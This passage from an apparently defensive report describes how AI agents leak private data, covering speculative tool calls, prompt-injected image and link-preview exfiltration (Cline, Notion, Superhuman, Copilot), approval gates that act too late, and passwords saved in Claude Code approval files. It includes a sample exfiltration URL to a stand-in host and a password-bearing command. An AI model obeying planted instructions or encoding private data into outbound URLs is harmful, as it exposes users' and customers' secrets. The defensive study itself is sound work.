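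Scores in the last column are lower partly because the adversary had to choose from 150 topics instead of 30. Random guessing would score less than 0.01 there.

The comparison between controls is convincing. Clean-up, read-only limits and allow-lists made almost no difference in any of the three tests, as the propositions predict, while rewriting and local substitutes always helped. The order stayed the same when two other models played the adversary, and on 66 tasks from AgentDojo, a test set made by other researchers. On the 20 sensitive AgentDojo tasks, the adversary scored 0.75 against both uncontrolled speculation and the read-only rule, and zero against rewriting and local substitutes.

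How much speculation itself reveals is less certain. With fixed plans it more than doubled the score, but with free planning the score rose only from 0.34 to 0.49. In the replay it rose only from 0.08 to 0.10, a difference that narrowly misses the usual threshold for statistical significance (p = 0.052). Mohammadi and colleagues reply that only the fixed plans hold the necessary calls constant and so isolate the effect of the ghost calls. This is a good reason to believe that ghost calls leak information, but it also means that the 0.97 comes from a set-up designed to make the leak visible. When the agent plans for itself, its necessary calls already reveal much of what the adversary can learn.

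The zeros for local substitutes are also less impressive because, in another run on the 150 tasks, that policy sent no calls to outside services, so the adversary had nothing to read.

To find out which part of a call reveals the topic, the researchers hid different parts of the calls in nine tasks. The adversary identified all nine topics from the arguments and tool names, five from the destinations and tool names, and three from the tool names alone. This helps explain why a filter that checked calls for personal identifiers before they went out did no better than no filter, scoring 0.12 in the replay. An argument such as "tenant rights lease termination penalty" reveals the topic without containing a name or phone number.

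Two smaller tests used real search services. With DuckDuckGo, rewriting reduced the adversary's score from 0.49 to 0.04 on 30 tasks run three times each. With Brave Search, the score fell only from 0.67 to 0.44 on nine tasks run once each. The adversary again judged the requests the agent had sent, so these tests confirm that rewriting works over a live connection but don't show what either company stores or infers.

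An observer inside the company may learn almost as much as the search service. Mohammadi and colleagues gave an adversary model only a shortened runtime log, with the tool's name, a 20-character summary of each argument (enough for "tenant rights lease"), the monitor's decision and a rough duration. Across all twelve policies, the model scored 0.24 with this log and 0.26 with the full requests. An adversary that saw only network traffic scored 0.04, about the same as random guessing, although few of the test's web addresses would have revealed a topic.

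All the main tasks are artificial, expanded by a language model from templates of sensitive topics, so the scores don't measure how often ordinary use exposes anything sensitive. The adversary also had a list of possible topics. When it had to name the topic without the list, its score across all policies on the 30 tasks fell from 0.33 to 0.13, even with credit for close paraphrases. A real search company has no such list, but it may have years of queries from the same person. A simple statistical classifier trained on labelled examples from these tasks scored 0.65, about twice as high as Opus, so an observer with relevant past data could do much better than the main results suggest.

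The crude labeller may also have made rewriting look more effective than it is, because marking every argument as sensitive leaves little for the monitor to miss. The researchers tested the opposite mistake by relabelling a fifth of the sensitive items as public. In the replay, with a smaller model as the adversary, rewriting then scored 0.06 and local substitutes 0.08, compared with 0.12 for no controls. Both still helped, but local substitutes no longer looked perfect.

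### What the protection costs

The controls did not noticeably harm the agent's answers. Each policy was tested on 30 tasks, run three times each, and a model graded the answers. Average success ranged from 0.77 to 0.83, with overlapping margins of error. It was highest without speculation, at 0.83, compared with 0.79 for both rewriting and local substitutes and 0.78 for uncontrolled speculation. On the same tasks, the adversary's score was 0.07 without speculation and 0.26 with uncontrolled speculation. With only 90 trials per policy, the test could easily have missed a drop in success of a few percentage points. It also used simulated tools, so it can't measure how much worse an agent does when an internal index replaces a real search engine.

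Speculation did not save much time in these tests either. With a single search tool, it reduced the median time per task from 8.39 to 7.94 seconds, but local substitutes eliminated that gain. On tasks with at least three parallel calls, it reduced the time by 12.3% without controls, 11.3% with rewriting and 9.6% with local substitutes.

Deferring every guess below the confidence threshold saved 12.9%, slightly more than sending every guess. This is odd because a threshold of 0.7 cut outside calls from about eight per task to one on the 150 replayed tasks. Differences of about one percentage point may well be noise. The paper also reports two adversary scores for that threshold on the same tasks, 0.08 and 0.05. Both are below the 0.10 for uncontrolled speculation, but because they differ, the size of the benefit is unclear.

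How much speed an operator loses by not guessing depends on how long the agent spends waiting for tools. If tools take up a fraction f of the total time, hiding all of that wait can make the agent at most 1/(1 − f) times as fast. At 60%, the limit is 2.5 times. *ETA* (2026) reports that for one agent that reasons at length before acting, tools took only 4.1% of the time, so perfect guessing could speed it up by at most 4.3%. An operator whose agent spends most of its time reasoning can therefore turn off speculative calls to outside services and lose little speed. A larger share of time spent on tools doesn't guarantee a large gain. In a web-browsing test described in *SPORK* (2026), tools took 37% of the time, but only 17% of the turns had a tool call long enough, at two seconds or more, for guessing to save much.

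Coding agents can often save time by running guessed commands without disclosing anything, because much of their waiting is for compilers and tests that run on the company's own machines. *TomasuLLM* (Yu, Huang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that runs guessed commands in private copies of the workspace, blocks anything that would send data over the network, and releases a result only if the agent later asks for exactly that action. The agent worked about 1.3 times as fast on three sets of coding tasks. The researchers designed these rules to keep the results correct and did not test privacy. Of the 20 faults they planted to test the checks, two involved network sends, and the system held back both. The same approach would do little for the tenant, whose assistant is waiting for the outside search.

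## Previews that contact outside servers

An agent with no search or email tool can still send private data out of a company by including a web address in its answer, if the program displaying the answer fetches whatever is at that address.

### How displaying an image sends data

A model usually adds a picture to an answer by writing the picture's web address in a notation called Markdown. The reader's chat window or browser then fetches the picture from that address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a website receives and commonly logs the whole address requested, so an attacker who gets a model to put private data in an address can read the data in the log.

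Suppose the billing company's coding agent opens a public help page about its table component. Someone has planted text on the page telling agents to end their answers with a logo and a note about their work. The agent wrongly treats this as part of its task and writes an address that includes a detail from the customer's record:

`https://pictures.example/logo.png?note=J-Smith-owes-412`

The server needs only the part before the question mark to find the picture, but the browser sends the rest as well.

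1. The agent writes its answer, including the address.
2. The developer's chat window starts to display the answer.
3. The window asks the server at pictures.example for the full address.
4. The server receives the request and logs it. **This is the moment of disclosure.**
5. The server returns a logo, a single transparent pixel or an error.
6. The developer reads the answer and decides whether to accept it.

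Encryption hides the address from networks along the way, but not from the stranger who runs the server. The developer can't prevent the disclosure by reading the answer carefully, because displaying the answer causes it. In the Notion AI case, covered in a later section, the image loaded before the user had answered a request for approval.

The main cases differ in who makes the request.

| Case | Who requests the address | Click needed? | What the user sees | What happened next |
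|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cline, a coding agent (2025) | the developer's chat window | no | an answer with an image | still unfixed over 90 days after the report |
| Amp, a coding agent (2025) | the developer's chat window | no | an answer with an image | quickly fixed |
| OpenClaw, a personal agent, on Telegram (2026) | Telegram's preview service | no | a message with a link and preview | users can turn previews off |
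| Microsoft 365 Copilot search (2026) | the user's browser, then Bing | one, to open the search | Copilot "thinking", then perhaps an odd answer | fixed on Microsoft's servers |
| Superhuman, an email program (reported December 2025) | the user's browser | no | an answer with an image | fixed within days, with later patches for related flaws |

### Images in coding tools

In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the security researcher Johann Rehberger recalls reporting this flaw to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, within months of ChatGPT's release. Microsoft restricted image loading in Bing Chat that May, and OpenAI added a first check in December. Researchers have since found dozens of similar flaws in other products.

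Coding agents make the flaw more serious because they can read files of passwords and keys. Embrace The Red's *Cline* describes a test in which a developer asked Cline to explain a file containing planted text. Cline read a separate file of secrets, then displayed an image whose address contained them. Requiring approval before Cline read files would have limited what it could collect, but anything already in the conversation would still have been at risk because Cline loaded images without asking.

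Rehberger reported this to Cline's developers on May 29, 2025. After 35 days without a response, he opened a public issue saying that nobody was reading security reports. The developers closed it the same day but did not discuss a fix, so Rehberger published the flaw after more than 90 days. Sourcegraph, which made Amp, received a report of the same flaw on June 14, 2025 and fixed it quickly, according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*.

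Other coding tools had the same default. Eclipse Foundation's *[Eclipse Theia] Data Exfiltration via Markdown Image Rendering in AI Chat* records that the AI chat in Theia, a platform for building coding tools, loaded images from any outside address before version 1.71.0. Willison, a programmer who tracks such cases, notes that Google classed image loading in its coding tool Antigravity as intended behavior when a researcher reported it. Google also publicly lists data theft through prompt injection in Antigravity as a known issue that it is working to fix.

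### Link previews in messages

Slack, Telegram and other messaging services often fetch a linked page to show its title and a thumbnail in the message. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, published in February 2026, points out that this sends the website the same kind of request as a click. If an agent posts a link with private data in its address, the service can send that data to whoever runs the website before the user clicks the link.

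Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* had demonstrated this in Slack in 2024. By default, Slack previews links in messages from both people and apps. When a test app posted a link, the linked website's log recorded a visit from Slack's preview bot. Because the bot runs on Slack's servers, the network records of a company using Slack might show only a message going to Slack.

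Developers can prevent the previews with two settings in the messages their app sends to Slack. OpenClaw has a similar setting for Telegram, but PromptArmor found that previews were on by default. With previews off, users lose the thumbnails, and they can still disclose the data by clicking the link. PromptArmor wants messaging services to let people turn off previews for a single chat or channel, so that people can keep previews in conversations without agents.

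In May 2026, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described a related risk in Cowork, an agent that works across a user's Microsoft 365 account. Cowork sent messages to its own user without asking permission, although Microsoft stated in its documentation that it asks before sending an email or posting in Teams. These messages can contain images from outside websites, which load when the user opens the message.

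In PromptArmor's test, the image addresses included download links that gave anyone who had them access to the user's files, so a short address could disclose a whole document. The attack worked in all five trials, and Cowork's activity display never showed the contents of the message. PromptArmor attributes the attack to the product's design rather than to a single bug. It recommends that administrators block downloads of sensitive files, but this also prevents staff from printing those files or opening them in the desktop version of Word.

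### Answers displayed before the filter has run

Chat programs usually display an answer as the model writes it. If a filter checks only the finished answer, the browser may fetch an image from an earlier part before the filter runs.

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes this flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot's company search, which covers email, meetings and files. A user had to click a link to a genuine Microsoft address that contained instructions for Copilot. Copilot then searched the user's mailbox and began writing an answer with an image address that contained the title of an email. The browser requested the image immediately, but Microsoft's filter turned the image code into harmless text only after Copilot had finished.

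Microsoft let the browser load images only from certain domains, so it would not have contacted an unknown website directly. But those domains included Bing, whose image search fetches pictures from other websites to analyze them. The browser sent the request to Bing, and Bing passed the email title to the stranger's server. Email titles can be sensitive, since some contain login codes that still work. Varonis says the same method could have disclosed meeting details and company files that Copilot had indexed.

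Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) lists the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 and says that Microsoft has fully fixed it and customers don't need to do anything. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, but it scored 6.5 out of 10 on the standard severity scale, a medium rating. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes the lower score to the required click.

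Varonis recommends cleaning each part of an answer before displaying it. Another option is to display the text as it arrives and hold back the images until the filter has checked the complete answer, which would delay only the images, and only slightly. A stop button is no substitute, since the browser can request an image before anyone notices that the answer looks strange.

### Limiting the permitted domains

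A website can send the browser a content security policy, a set of rules that can list the domains from which the page may load images. If the billing company's chat window had such a list and pictures.example was not on it, the browser would refuse to make the request in step 3. The browser enforces the list, so the protection works even if the agent has followed the planted text.

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) compared a limit on domains with warnings to the model. It tested each defense 30 times on an agent that had a tool for making web requests and received a preview of a web page containing planted instructions.

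| Defense | Share of runs that leaked data |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Marking outside text as untrusted | 100% |
| Telling the model never to follow instructions from web pages | 67% |
| Both warnings | 57% |
| Allowing requests only to listed domains | 0% |

The agent tried to send the data in every run with the domain limit, and the limit blocked it each time. Lan and colleagues deliberately used an address that was clearly not on the list of allowed domains, so the result shows that the block works but not that a real company's list would be safe. They also tested only one small model, Qwen 2.5 with 7 billion parameters, and put the secret directly in its context, which made leaks more likely.

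Filters that looked for suspicious addresses or secret-like text also reduced leaks to zero, but those results are less convincing. One filter blocked addresses containing the word "collect", which appears in the attack addresses that Lan and colleagues describe. With another filter, the agent stopped trying to send the data. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided text that would trigger the filter, but a filter that acts after the model has written a request should not affect what the model writes.

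A list of allowed domains can fail in practice, as PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* shows. It describes a user who asked the assistant in Superhuman, an email program, to summarize messages from the last hour. One of them, which the user had not opened, contained planted instructions. Superhuman's policy blocked images from unknown domains but allowed docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms.

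Google Forms can accept answers as part of a web address. The assistant put the contents of other emails into such an address and presented it as an image. When the browser tried to load the image, Google recorded the emails as answers to the attacker's form, where the attacker could read them without running a server or searching its logs. PromptArmor obtained the full contents of several emails in one response and parts of over 40 emails in another.

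PromptArmor reported the flaw on Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on Monday and deployed a first patch on Tuesday. It fixed other parts of the product later that month and in January 2026, before the two companies published the case on January 12.

People other than a server's owner may be able to read data sent to its domain. The owner of a permitted service may let any customer store data on it, as Google did, or the service may request addresses on other servers, as Bing did. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes an earlier case of the second problem in Microsoft's Copilot, in which a permitted Teams preview service passed data to an outside server. Microsoft fixed that flaw in May 2025, about a year before it published the one involving Bing.

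The owner of a domain can also change. In a case that Willison recounted in September 2025, the security company Noma found that Salesforce's list of permitted domains for its AI agents still included one whose registration had expired. Noma registered the domain and received customers' contact details in a test. Salesforce then corrected the list and restricted the addresses that its agents could include in answers. So a company has to keep checking what each permitted service can do and who owns it.

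### Image proxies and known addresses

An image proxy fetches pictures on the reader's behalf, so the outside server sees the proxy's network address instead of the reader's. This protects the reader's location. But if the proxy accepts any image address, it still sends the note about J. Smith's debt to pictures.example.

GitHub's image proxy is stricter. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains that GitHub signs the address of each outside image when it processes a document, and that the proxy refuses any address without a valid signature. An agent therefore can't simply add a customer's balance to an address as it writes. But Legit Security showed in 2025 that GitHub's Copilot Chat could still leak private code, because the choice of which signed images to load can carry information. GitHub responded by turning off images in Copilot Chat completely by August 14.

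OpenAI instead checks addresses against an index of public web addresses, which its crawler builds without access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT may automatically load an address only if it exactly matches an entry. The index might include the plain address of the logo but should not include the version that mentions J. Smith. If there is no match, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns the user that the address may contain information from the conversation.

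OpenAI chose this method partly because a fixed list of trusted websites would cause too many warnings, and people who see warnings often learn to click through them. This method must also warn about some harmless addresses, such as a company's private preview page, which a public crawler should never have encountered. Whoever reads the warning then has to decide whether the address is safe.

This method has a weakness similar to GitHub's proxy, since an agent can disclose a little through its choice of indexed pages. Embrace The Red's review of OpenAI's technical paper notes that OpenAI acknowledges this weakness. The review suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. It calls OpenAI's method a significant improvement but warns that the company's developers may not apply it everywhere. OpenAI's 2023 check was at first missing from its Mac and iPhone apps.

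Blocking all outside images is simpler and prevents leaks through image loading, but users lose charts, screenshots and other pictures. Blocking images also doesn't stop requests the agent makes itself. PromptArmor found that Superhuman's assistant could disclose emails through its web search feature as well, because it could open any web address. A company that blocks images therefore needs a separate limit on the agent's web tools, and another on previews in any messaging service where the agent posts.

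### Demonstrations and known theft

All the leaks described here come from researchers' tests. Microsoft's advisory marks CVE-2026-42824 as not exploited, and Reddy and Gujral report no evidence that anyone used the earlier Copilot flaw against real victims. Security companies found many of these flaws, and several of those companies sell protection against such attacks, so they have a reason to make the flaws sound alarming.

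Software companies sometimes dispute reports of these flaws. In April 2026, Noma reported a flaw in the AI assistant of Grafana, a company that makes monitoring software. Grafana fixed the flaw but disputed the claim that the attack needed no action from the user. Its security chief, Joe McManus, told CyberScoop that the user would have had to tell the assistant repeatedly to follow malicious instructions, even after it had warned about them. McManus also said there was no evidence that real attackers had exploited the flaw and that no data had leaked from Grafana's cloud service.

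Google looked for real attacks by searching archived copies of the public web for common prompt injection phrases, and published the results in April 2026. Each monthly archive contains two to three billion pages. Google found only a few attempts to steal data, mostly simple ones, and little sign that attackers were using the more advanced methods researchers had published in 2025. But malicious injections of all kinds, including attempts to delete files, rose by 32% from November 2025 to February 2026.

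The search did not cover private emails or most social media, and it may have missed unusual wording. It also counted planted instructions, not successful thefts, which are harder to find. In 95% of the successful attacks in Lan and colleagues' main experiment of 480 runs, the agent's final answer gave no sign that it had sent any data, so a company that keeps only its agents' answers would have missed nearly all of those leaks.

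## What approval gates do and do not hold back

An approval gate can prevent a disclosure only if the person answers before the data leaves. Some products save the agent's work, display it and then ask whether to keep it. This order works well for text that the software can restore, because people judge an edit more easily when they see it in place. But if displaying the edit contacts an outside server, the product asks too late to prevent the disclosure.

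Suppose the billing company's agent proposes adding a picture to an internal page, and the picture's web address contains a customer's balance. Displaying it sends the whole address to the server that hosts the picture.

| Step | Ask first | Save first |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The agent proposes the edit | The agent proposes the edit |
| 2 | The software shows the address as plain text and waits | The software saves the edit and displays the page |
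| 3 | The developer refuses | The browser requests the picture. **The server now has the balance.** |
| 4 | The software discards the proposal | The software asks for approval |
| 5 | | The developer refuses, and the software removes the picture |

The page ends up the same in both cases, so looking at it afterwards would not reveal that the balance had left the company.

Asking for approval before saving can prevent the disclosure only if the approval prompt does not load the image, because a live preview leaks the balance just as saving first does. The developer also has to spot the balance in what may be a very long address. Unlike saving first, asking first still gives a careful reviewer a chance to prevent the disclosure.

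### Notion's hiring tracker

PromptArmor's *Notion AI*, published in January 2026, describes a test of the assistant in Notion, a program for shared documents. The assistant can edit pages, and Notion saved its edits before the user approved them.

1. A user uploads a candidate's résumé and asks the assistant to update the notes in a hiring tracker. The résumé contains hidden text that the assistant wrongly treats as instructions.
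2. The assistant gathers all the text in the tracker, puts it into a web address and inserts an image with that address into the page.
3. Notion saves the edit, and the user's browser requests the image. **This is the moment of disclosure.**
4. Notion warns the user about an untrusted website and asks for approval.
5. The user accepts or refuses. The stranger's server has the data either way.

The data included salary expectations, feedback on candidates, details of internal roles and diversity hiring goals. The warning displayed the address with the tracker's text in it, so an attentive user could have understood what was wrong and refused. That user would reasonably have thought the refusal had worked, and so would have had no reason to report a leak.

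Notion also used a model to scan uploaded documents and warn about suspicious ones. PromptArmor did not focus on this check because the same hidden text could come from a web page or another source that Notion did not appear to scan.

A related flaw affected Notion Mail's email-drafting assistant. If a user asked for a draft based on two Notion pages, planted text in one could make the assistant add an image whose address contained material from the other. The browser would request the image when the draft appeared, before the user decided whether to send the email. Less data was at risk than with the main assistant, because the drafting assistant seemed able to read only the Notion sources the user mentioned.

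PromptArmor reported the problem on December 24, 2025 through HackerOne, a company that handles security reports for other organizations. HackerOne's staff asked for a different format, and PromptArmor supplied it the same day. On December 29, HackerOne's staff closed the report as "Not Applicable". PromptArmor published its findings on January 7, 2026. Notion contacted PromptArmor that day to explain that the report had not reached its own team, and had deployed a fix for document edits by that night. PromptArmor's timeline does not mention a separate fix for email drafts.

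PromptArmor recommended that Notion get users' explicit approval before loading outside images in the assistant's page edits, and that it not load them automatically in email drafts. Notion also lets users require confirmation before the assistant makes web requests. That setting is part of the assistant's web search, so it probably would not have stopped the user's browser from requesting an image.

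### Actions that need no approval

Coding agents generally ask for approval before acting. Anthropic explains that a permission prompt in Claude Code shows what the agent is about to do and waits for an answer. But an approval gate holds back only the actions it covers, and the usual settings let agents read files without asking.

| Product and setting | What runs without a question | What it can reveal |
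|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Manual mode | reading and searching files in the project folder, and shell commands on a read-only list | file contents, to the model provider and anyone who can read the saved transcript |
| Claude Code, accept-edits mode | the same, plus file edits and common file commands | private data that the agent copies into a file and someone later uploads |
| Claude Code, auto mode | nearly everything, with checks by a second model | whatever those checks miss, including data in requests to outside services |
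| OpenAI's Codex, default local setting | reading files, editing the project folder and running routine local commands | file contents, to the model provider |
| Notion AI, before the January fix | saving an edit and loading its images | page contents, to the server that hosts the image |

The setting in use often depends on how the customer pays. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, Claude Code normally starts in auto mode for people on the Pro, Max and Team plans, and in Manual mode for those on an Enterprise plan or paying through an API key. In auto mode, the second model reviews most actions in place of the user, so for many developers no person is involved in approving those actions.

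Even in Manual mode, the strictest of these settings, the agent would not ask the billing company's developer for approval before opening a project file containing a customer's record. The first request might come only when the agent tried to upload its branch, after the model provider had received the record. Claude Code's reading tools do require approval to open files outside the project folder. An optional setting extends this requirement to shell commands that read files, even in auto mode.

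Anthropic's list of exceptions shows that reading can be risky. On Windows, Claude Code asks before running a read-only command on a file at a network address, because opening the file can send the user's Windows credentials to the computer at that address. It also asks before listing active programs if the output could include their environment variables, which often contain passwords. Neither command changes anything, so a rule based only on reversibility would allow both without approval.

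The strictest rules guard against destructive actions. No Claude Code mode automatically approves deleting certain critical folders. Codex requires approval for any call to a connected tool whose own description marks it as destructive, even if the description also marks it as read-only.

Codex handles disclosure mainly by limiting where data can go. By default, OpenAI turns off network access for the commands Codex runs, and Codex asks when it needs to go beyond the project folder or the other limits of its sandbox, the restricted environment in which those commands run. As of March 2026, its web search also used an index that OpenAI maintains. OpenAI sees the queries, but it normally runs the model too, so searching the index adds no new observer, while a live search would add at least one.

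OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes the company's internal network rules, which allow connections to expected destinations, block some others and require approval for unfamiliar domains. OpenAI notes that administrators can also make particular files unreadable to the agent, which protects passwords even from the model provider. The agent then can't do any task that needs those files.

Developers who build their own agents must set such limits themselves. OpenAI's guide for them, *Sandbox security*, warns that code written by an agent can use any files, credentials and network connections in the environment where it runs. The guide recommends giving users who must not share data separate environments, and allowing outbound connections only to approved addresses.

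A saved approval can cover more than the user intended. If a developer tells Claude Code not to ask again before fetching pages from a particular domain, the permission limits where later requests go but not what they contain. Anthropic warns that restricting the page-fetching tool does not prevent network access if the agent is allowed to run shell commands, and it recommends enforcing network limits through the sandbox.

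Some data leaves without being part of any action the user approves. Ganglani (2026), in *Claude Code 'Don't Ask Again' Leaked 1,122 Secrets*, reports that until a fix in November 2026, Claude Code included the user's account email address in every web request it made. The address was in a header, a part of the request that the website receives but people rarely look at. A developer who checked the web address carefully before approving the request would still have disclosed their email address to the website. Sonar's *Your secrets are leaking to AI coding agents* describes a larger case, in which a researcher caught xAI's coding agent Grok Build uploading developers' entire repositories to cloud storage. The upload included an unredacted test password. Asking users to approve individual commands does little to prevent such uploads, because the program itself sends the files.

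### Passwords in saved approvals

The gate's own records can leak as well. Suppose the billing company's agent needs to look up an account, which requires the database password. It proposes a command like this one:

`PGPASSWORD=example-password psql -h db.example.com`

Claude Code asks a developer whether to run a command that contains a password. The developer expects to see the same question twenty times that day and chooses "Yes, and don't ask again". Claude Code then saves the approval as a rule in the project's `.claude/settings.local.json` file. The rule is sometimes a general pattern, but TechSpot's *Claude Code's "don't ask again" button is leaking passwords and API keys* (2026) explains that it is often the exact command. In that case, the file contains the password in plain text, and anyone who uploads it with the rest of the project publishes the password too.

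In November 2026, the security company Apiiro reported finding 2,539 different secrets in 1,994 public GitHub repositories, most of them in these approval files (Cornelißen, *Claude Code speichert Passwörter in Freigaben*, 2026; Slashdot, *Claude Code's 'Don't Ask Again' File Exposes Passwords and Keys*, 2026). Current copies of those files contained 1,379 of the secrets. Another 734 had been deleted from the current version but remained in Git history. The other 426 came from settings files that teams share on purpose and from saved transcripts of agent sessions.

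More than a third of the secrets in the current files gave direct access to a database. Apiiro also found logins for public servers, AWS keys and the owner password for a database of medical records. In half of the affected repositories, the material had been public for at least 217 days.

Of the 104,185 public approval files Apiiro found, 1,122 (1.1%) contained a secret. The share rose with file size, from fewer than one in 500 files under 500 bytes to one in ten over 8 kilobytes. Files grow as approvals accumulate, so the developers most at risk are those who have used the agent longest on a project and approved the most commands.

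Apiiro did not test whether the secrets still worked, although one company it notified confirmed that its key did. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) reports on an earlier search by the security company Lakera, which scanned about 46,500 packages on npm, a public library of JavaScript code. Lakera found the file in 428 packages, and 33 of those files, or about one in 13, contained working credentials. This rate is much higher than on GitHub, but it comes from a far smaller sample.

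Anthropic intends the file to stay on the developer's computer. When Claude Code creates it in a Git repository, it adds the file to that computer's global ignore list, which tells Git to leave it out of uploads. The protection can fail in several ways:

- The project folder becomes a Git repository only after Claude Code has created the file.
- Someone copies the project to another computer, which does not have the same ignore list.
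- Someone has already committed the file. Git then keeps tracking it whatever the ignore list says, and later commits can include each new approval.

Claude Code does not add its settings file to the project's own ignore list, which is copied with the project. The agent itself may also commit the file. Apiiro traced 1,105 of the repositories and found that a commit listing Claude as a co-author had changed the file in 539 of them. Claude Code's commit instructions warn the model against including two common kinds of password file, but not the settings file.

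A developer may approve a command without noticing that it exposes secrets. A consultant at the security firm ironPeak describes approving commands after glancing at them for half a second, and discovering only later that a file containing database passwords and keys was in the repository's history.

Automated scanners miss many of these secrets. Two widely used ones, gitleaks and TruffleHog, both failed to flag 215 of the 1,122 files. They look mainly for keys with a recognizable prefix and a random string, but a password someone made up can look like any other word in a command.

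Apiiro reproduced the problem with recent models, including Claude Opus 5.5, so a better model alone does not solve it. The cause is how Claude Code stores approvals. Of the 16 coding agents Apiiro examined, only Claude Code saved the full command in a project file by default.

The exact wording does, however, keep the permission narrow. Claude Code offers the "don't ask again" option only when the question can show everything the new rule would allow, and a rule without a wildcard permits only one command. A broader rule that allowed every `psql` command would not need to contain the password, but it would let the agent read or alter the whole database without asking. So the narrowest permission can also reveal the most if it leaks. Cornelißen recommends keeping the password in a secret manager and having the command refer to it by a variable name, so that the saved rule contains only the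 name.

### Anthropic's reply

Boris Cherny, who heads Claude Code at Anthropic, answered on the discussion site Hacker News on November 7, 2026. Cherny acknowledged that Claude Code had not removed secrets from its files in the past and said the team was looking into ways to prevent this. But Cherny argued that people should not put this file under version control. Claude Code adds the file to an ignore list when it creates it, so Cherny concluded that "the files were manually created and checked in".

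Some of the exposed files may well have got there that way, but Apiiro's findings suggest that not all of them did. The ignore list can still miss a file that Claude Code created, in the ways described above, and Claude co-authored commits that changed the file in almost half of the repositories traced. Co-authorship does not prove that the agent chose to include the file, since a developer may have told it to commit everything.

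Cherny called permission rules "old hat" and recommended auto mode, which prompts people less often and so leaves them fewer approvals to save. When a reader pointed out that auto mode can still prompt for approval of a sensitive command and save that approval, Cherny replied "good catch". Anthropic planned to try making auto mode catch such cases and adding a basic scan for secrets, but gave no date. The scan would need to detect ordinary passwords as well as standard keys, or it would miss the same files as the existing tools.

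Users had reported the behavior on August 11, 2025. A bot closed that report in January 2026 after 60 days without activity. According to Apiiro, Anthropic did not reply to three later reports either.

### The unapproved reply at Meta

In March 2026, an agent at Meta answered an employee's technical question on an internal forum without approval, and the harm came from what a colleague did with the answer. According to The Information, which saw Meta's incident report, a software engineer had used the in-house agent to analyze the question, and the agent then posted its advice publicly within the company. Slashdot's *Rogue AI Triggers Serious Security Incident At Meta* (2026) quotes The Verge's report that only the engineer was supposed to see the reply.

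The advice in the post was wrong, and another employee followed it. The resulting change gave engineers access to sensitive company and user data they were not authorized to see. The access lasted almost two hours, according to The Decoder's *A rogue AI agent caused a serious security incident at Meta*, and Meta gave the incident its second-highest severity rating. No report suggests that the post itself contained private data.

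Meta's spokesperson, Tracy Clayton, attributed the exposure to the employee who made the change. Landymore's *Rogue AI Agent Triggers Emergency at Meta* quotes Clayton as saying that the agent "took no action aside from providing a response to a question". Clayton also said that a footer labeled the post as automated, that the employee's reply showed they knew this, and that further checks would have prevented the incident. According to Meta, nobody mishandled user data, and the company had no evidence that anyone had exploited the access.

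Clayton is right that a person, not the agent, opened the data. But posting to a forum is also an action, because it shows a draft to people who may act on it. Deleting the post later would not have reversed the change the second employee had already made.

Asking for the engineer's approval before posting might not have helped. The Verge could not establish whether the engineer had planned to share the answer anyway, and an engineer who missed the mistake would probably have approved it. A separate check on the change to data access would have protected the data more directly, whether the bad advice came from an agent or a colleague.

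## Pull requests, comments and screenshots prepared for reviewers

Opening a pull request shows the proposed change to everyone who can read the repository, before any reviewer has approved it. Those readers are usually colleagues and contractors if the repository is private, and include anyone with an internet connection if it is public. They can also see the description, screenshots and reviewers' comments, which all appear on the same page.

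### What "draft" and "secret" mean on GitHub

On GitHub, marking a pull request as a draft means it is not ready to merge, but does not change who can open the page. GitHub's *About pull requests* explains that GitHub does not automatically ask code owners, the people responsible for the affected files, to review a draft until its author marks it as ready.

GitHub's *Introducing draft pull requests* suggests using a draft for work such as a hackathon project that the author never intends to merge but would like others to try out and comment on. Until May 2025, people on GitHub's free plan could create drafts only in public repositories, according to GitHub's *Draft pull requests are now available in all repositories* (2025), so for about six years every draft on that plan was public.

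GitHub also hosts gists, small pages for sharing code or text. A secret gist does not appear in GitHub's public listing, and only its author can find it by searching. But GitHub's *Creating gists* warns that secret gists "aren't private", because anyone who has or finds the address can read them. In November 2025, GitHub (2025) began reporting keys found in secret gists to the companies that issued them. It said the belief that secret gists are private is a common misconception, and advised people to treat a key leaked in one like any other public leak.

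| Item | Who can read it | What the label changes |
|---|---|---|
| Pull request, and comments on it | anyone who can read the repository | |
| Draft pull request, and comments on it | anyone who can read the repository | nobody can merge it, and code owners get no automatic request |
| Secret gist | anyone who has or finds the address | it stays out of listings and other people's searches |
| Public gist | anyone | people can browse and search for it |

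Each gist is a Git repository, so readers can copy it and look through its earlier versions, including lines the author has since deleted. The author can make a secret gist public, but not the reverse.

Suppose the billing company's agent has a long error log to show a reviewer, and the log includes the customer's record. The agent uses GitHub's command-line program to save the log as a secret gist, then puts the link in a comment on the pull request. Even if only three people can read the repository, anyone they forward the link to can open the log.

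People also take less care when they think only colleagues will see their work. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) reports that 32.2% of the internal repositories the company monitored in 2025 contained at least one secret, compared with 5.6% of the public ones. One wrong visibility setting can therefore expose secrets that have accumulated over years.

### Glow's screenshot investigation

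In September 2026, Glow reported finding over 13,000 internal images in more than 900 public GitHub repositories. The images came from developers at more than 300 organizations. *AI agents leak 13K screenshots from 343 tech firms* (Corvin, 2026) gives the number as 343. These organizations included the manufacturer whose agent published a utility company's billing records. Glow did not name the others, but they included a Fortune 500 travel company, a leading AI lab and one of the world's largest technology companies.

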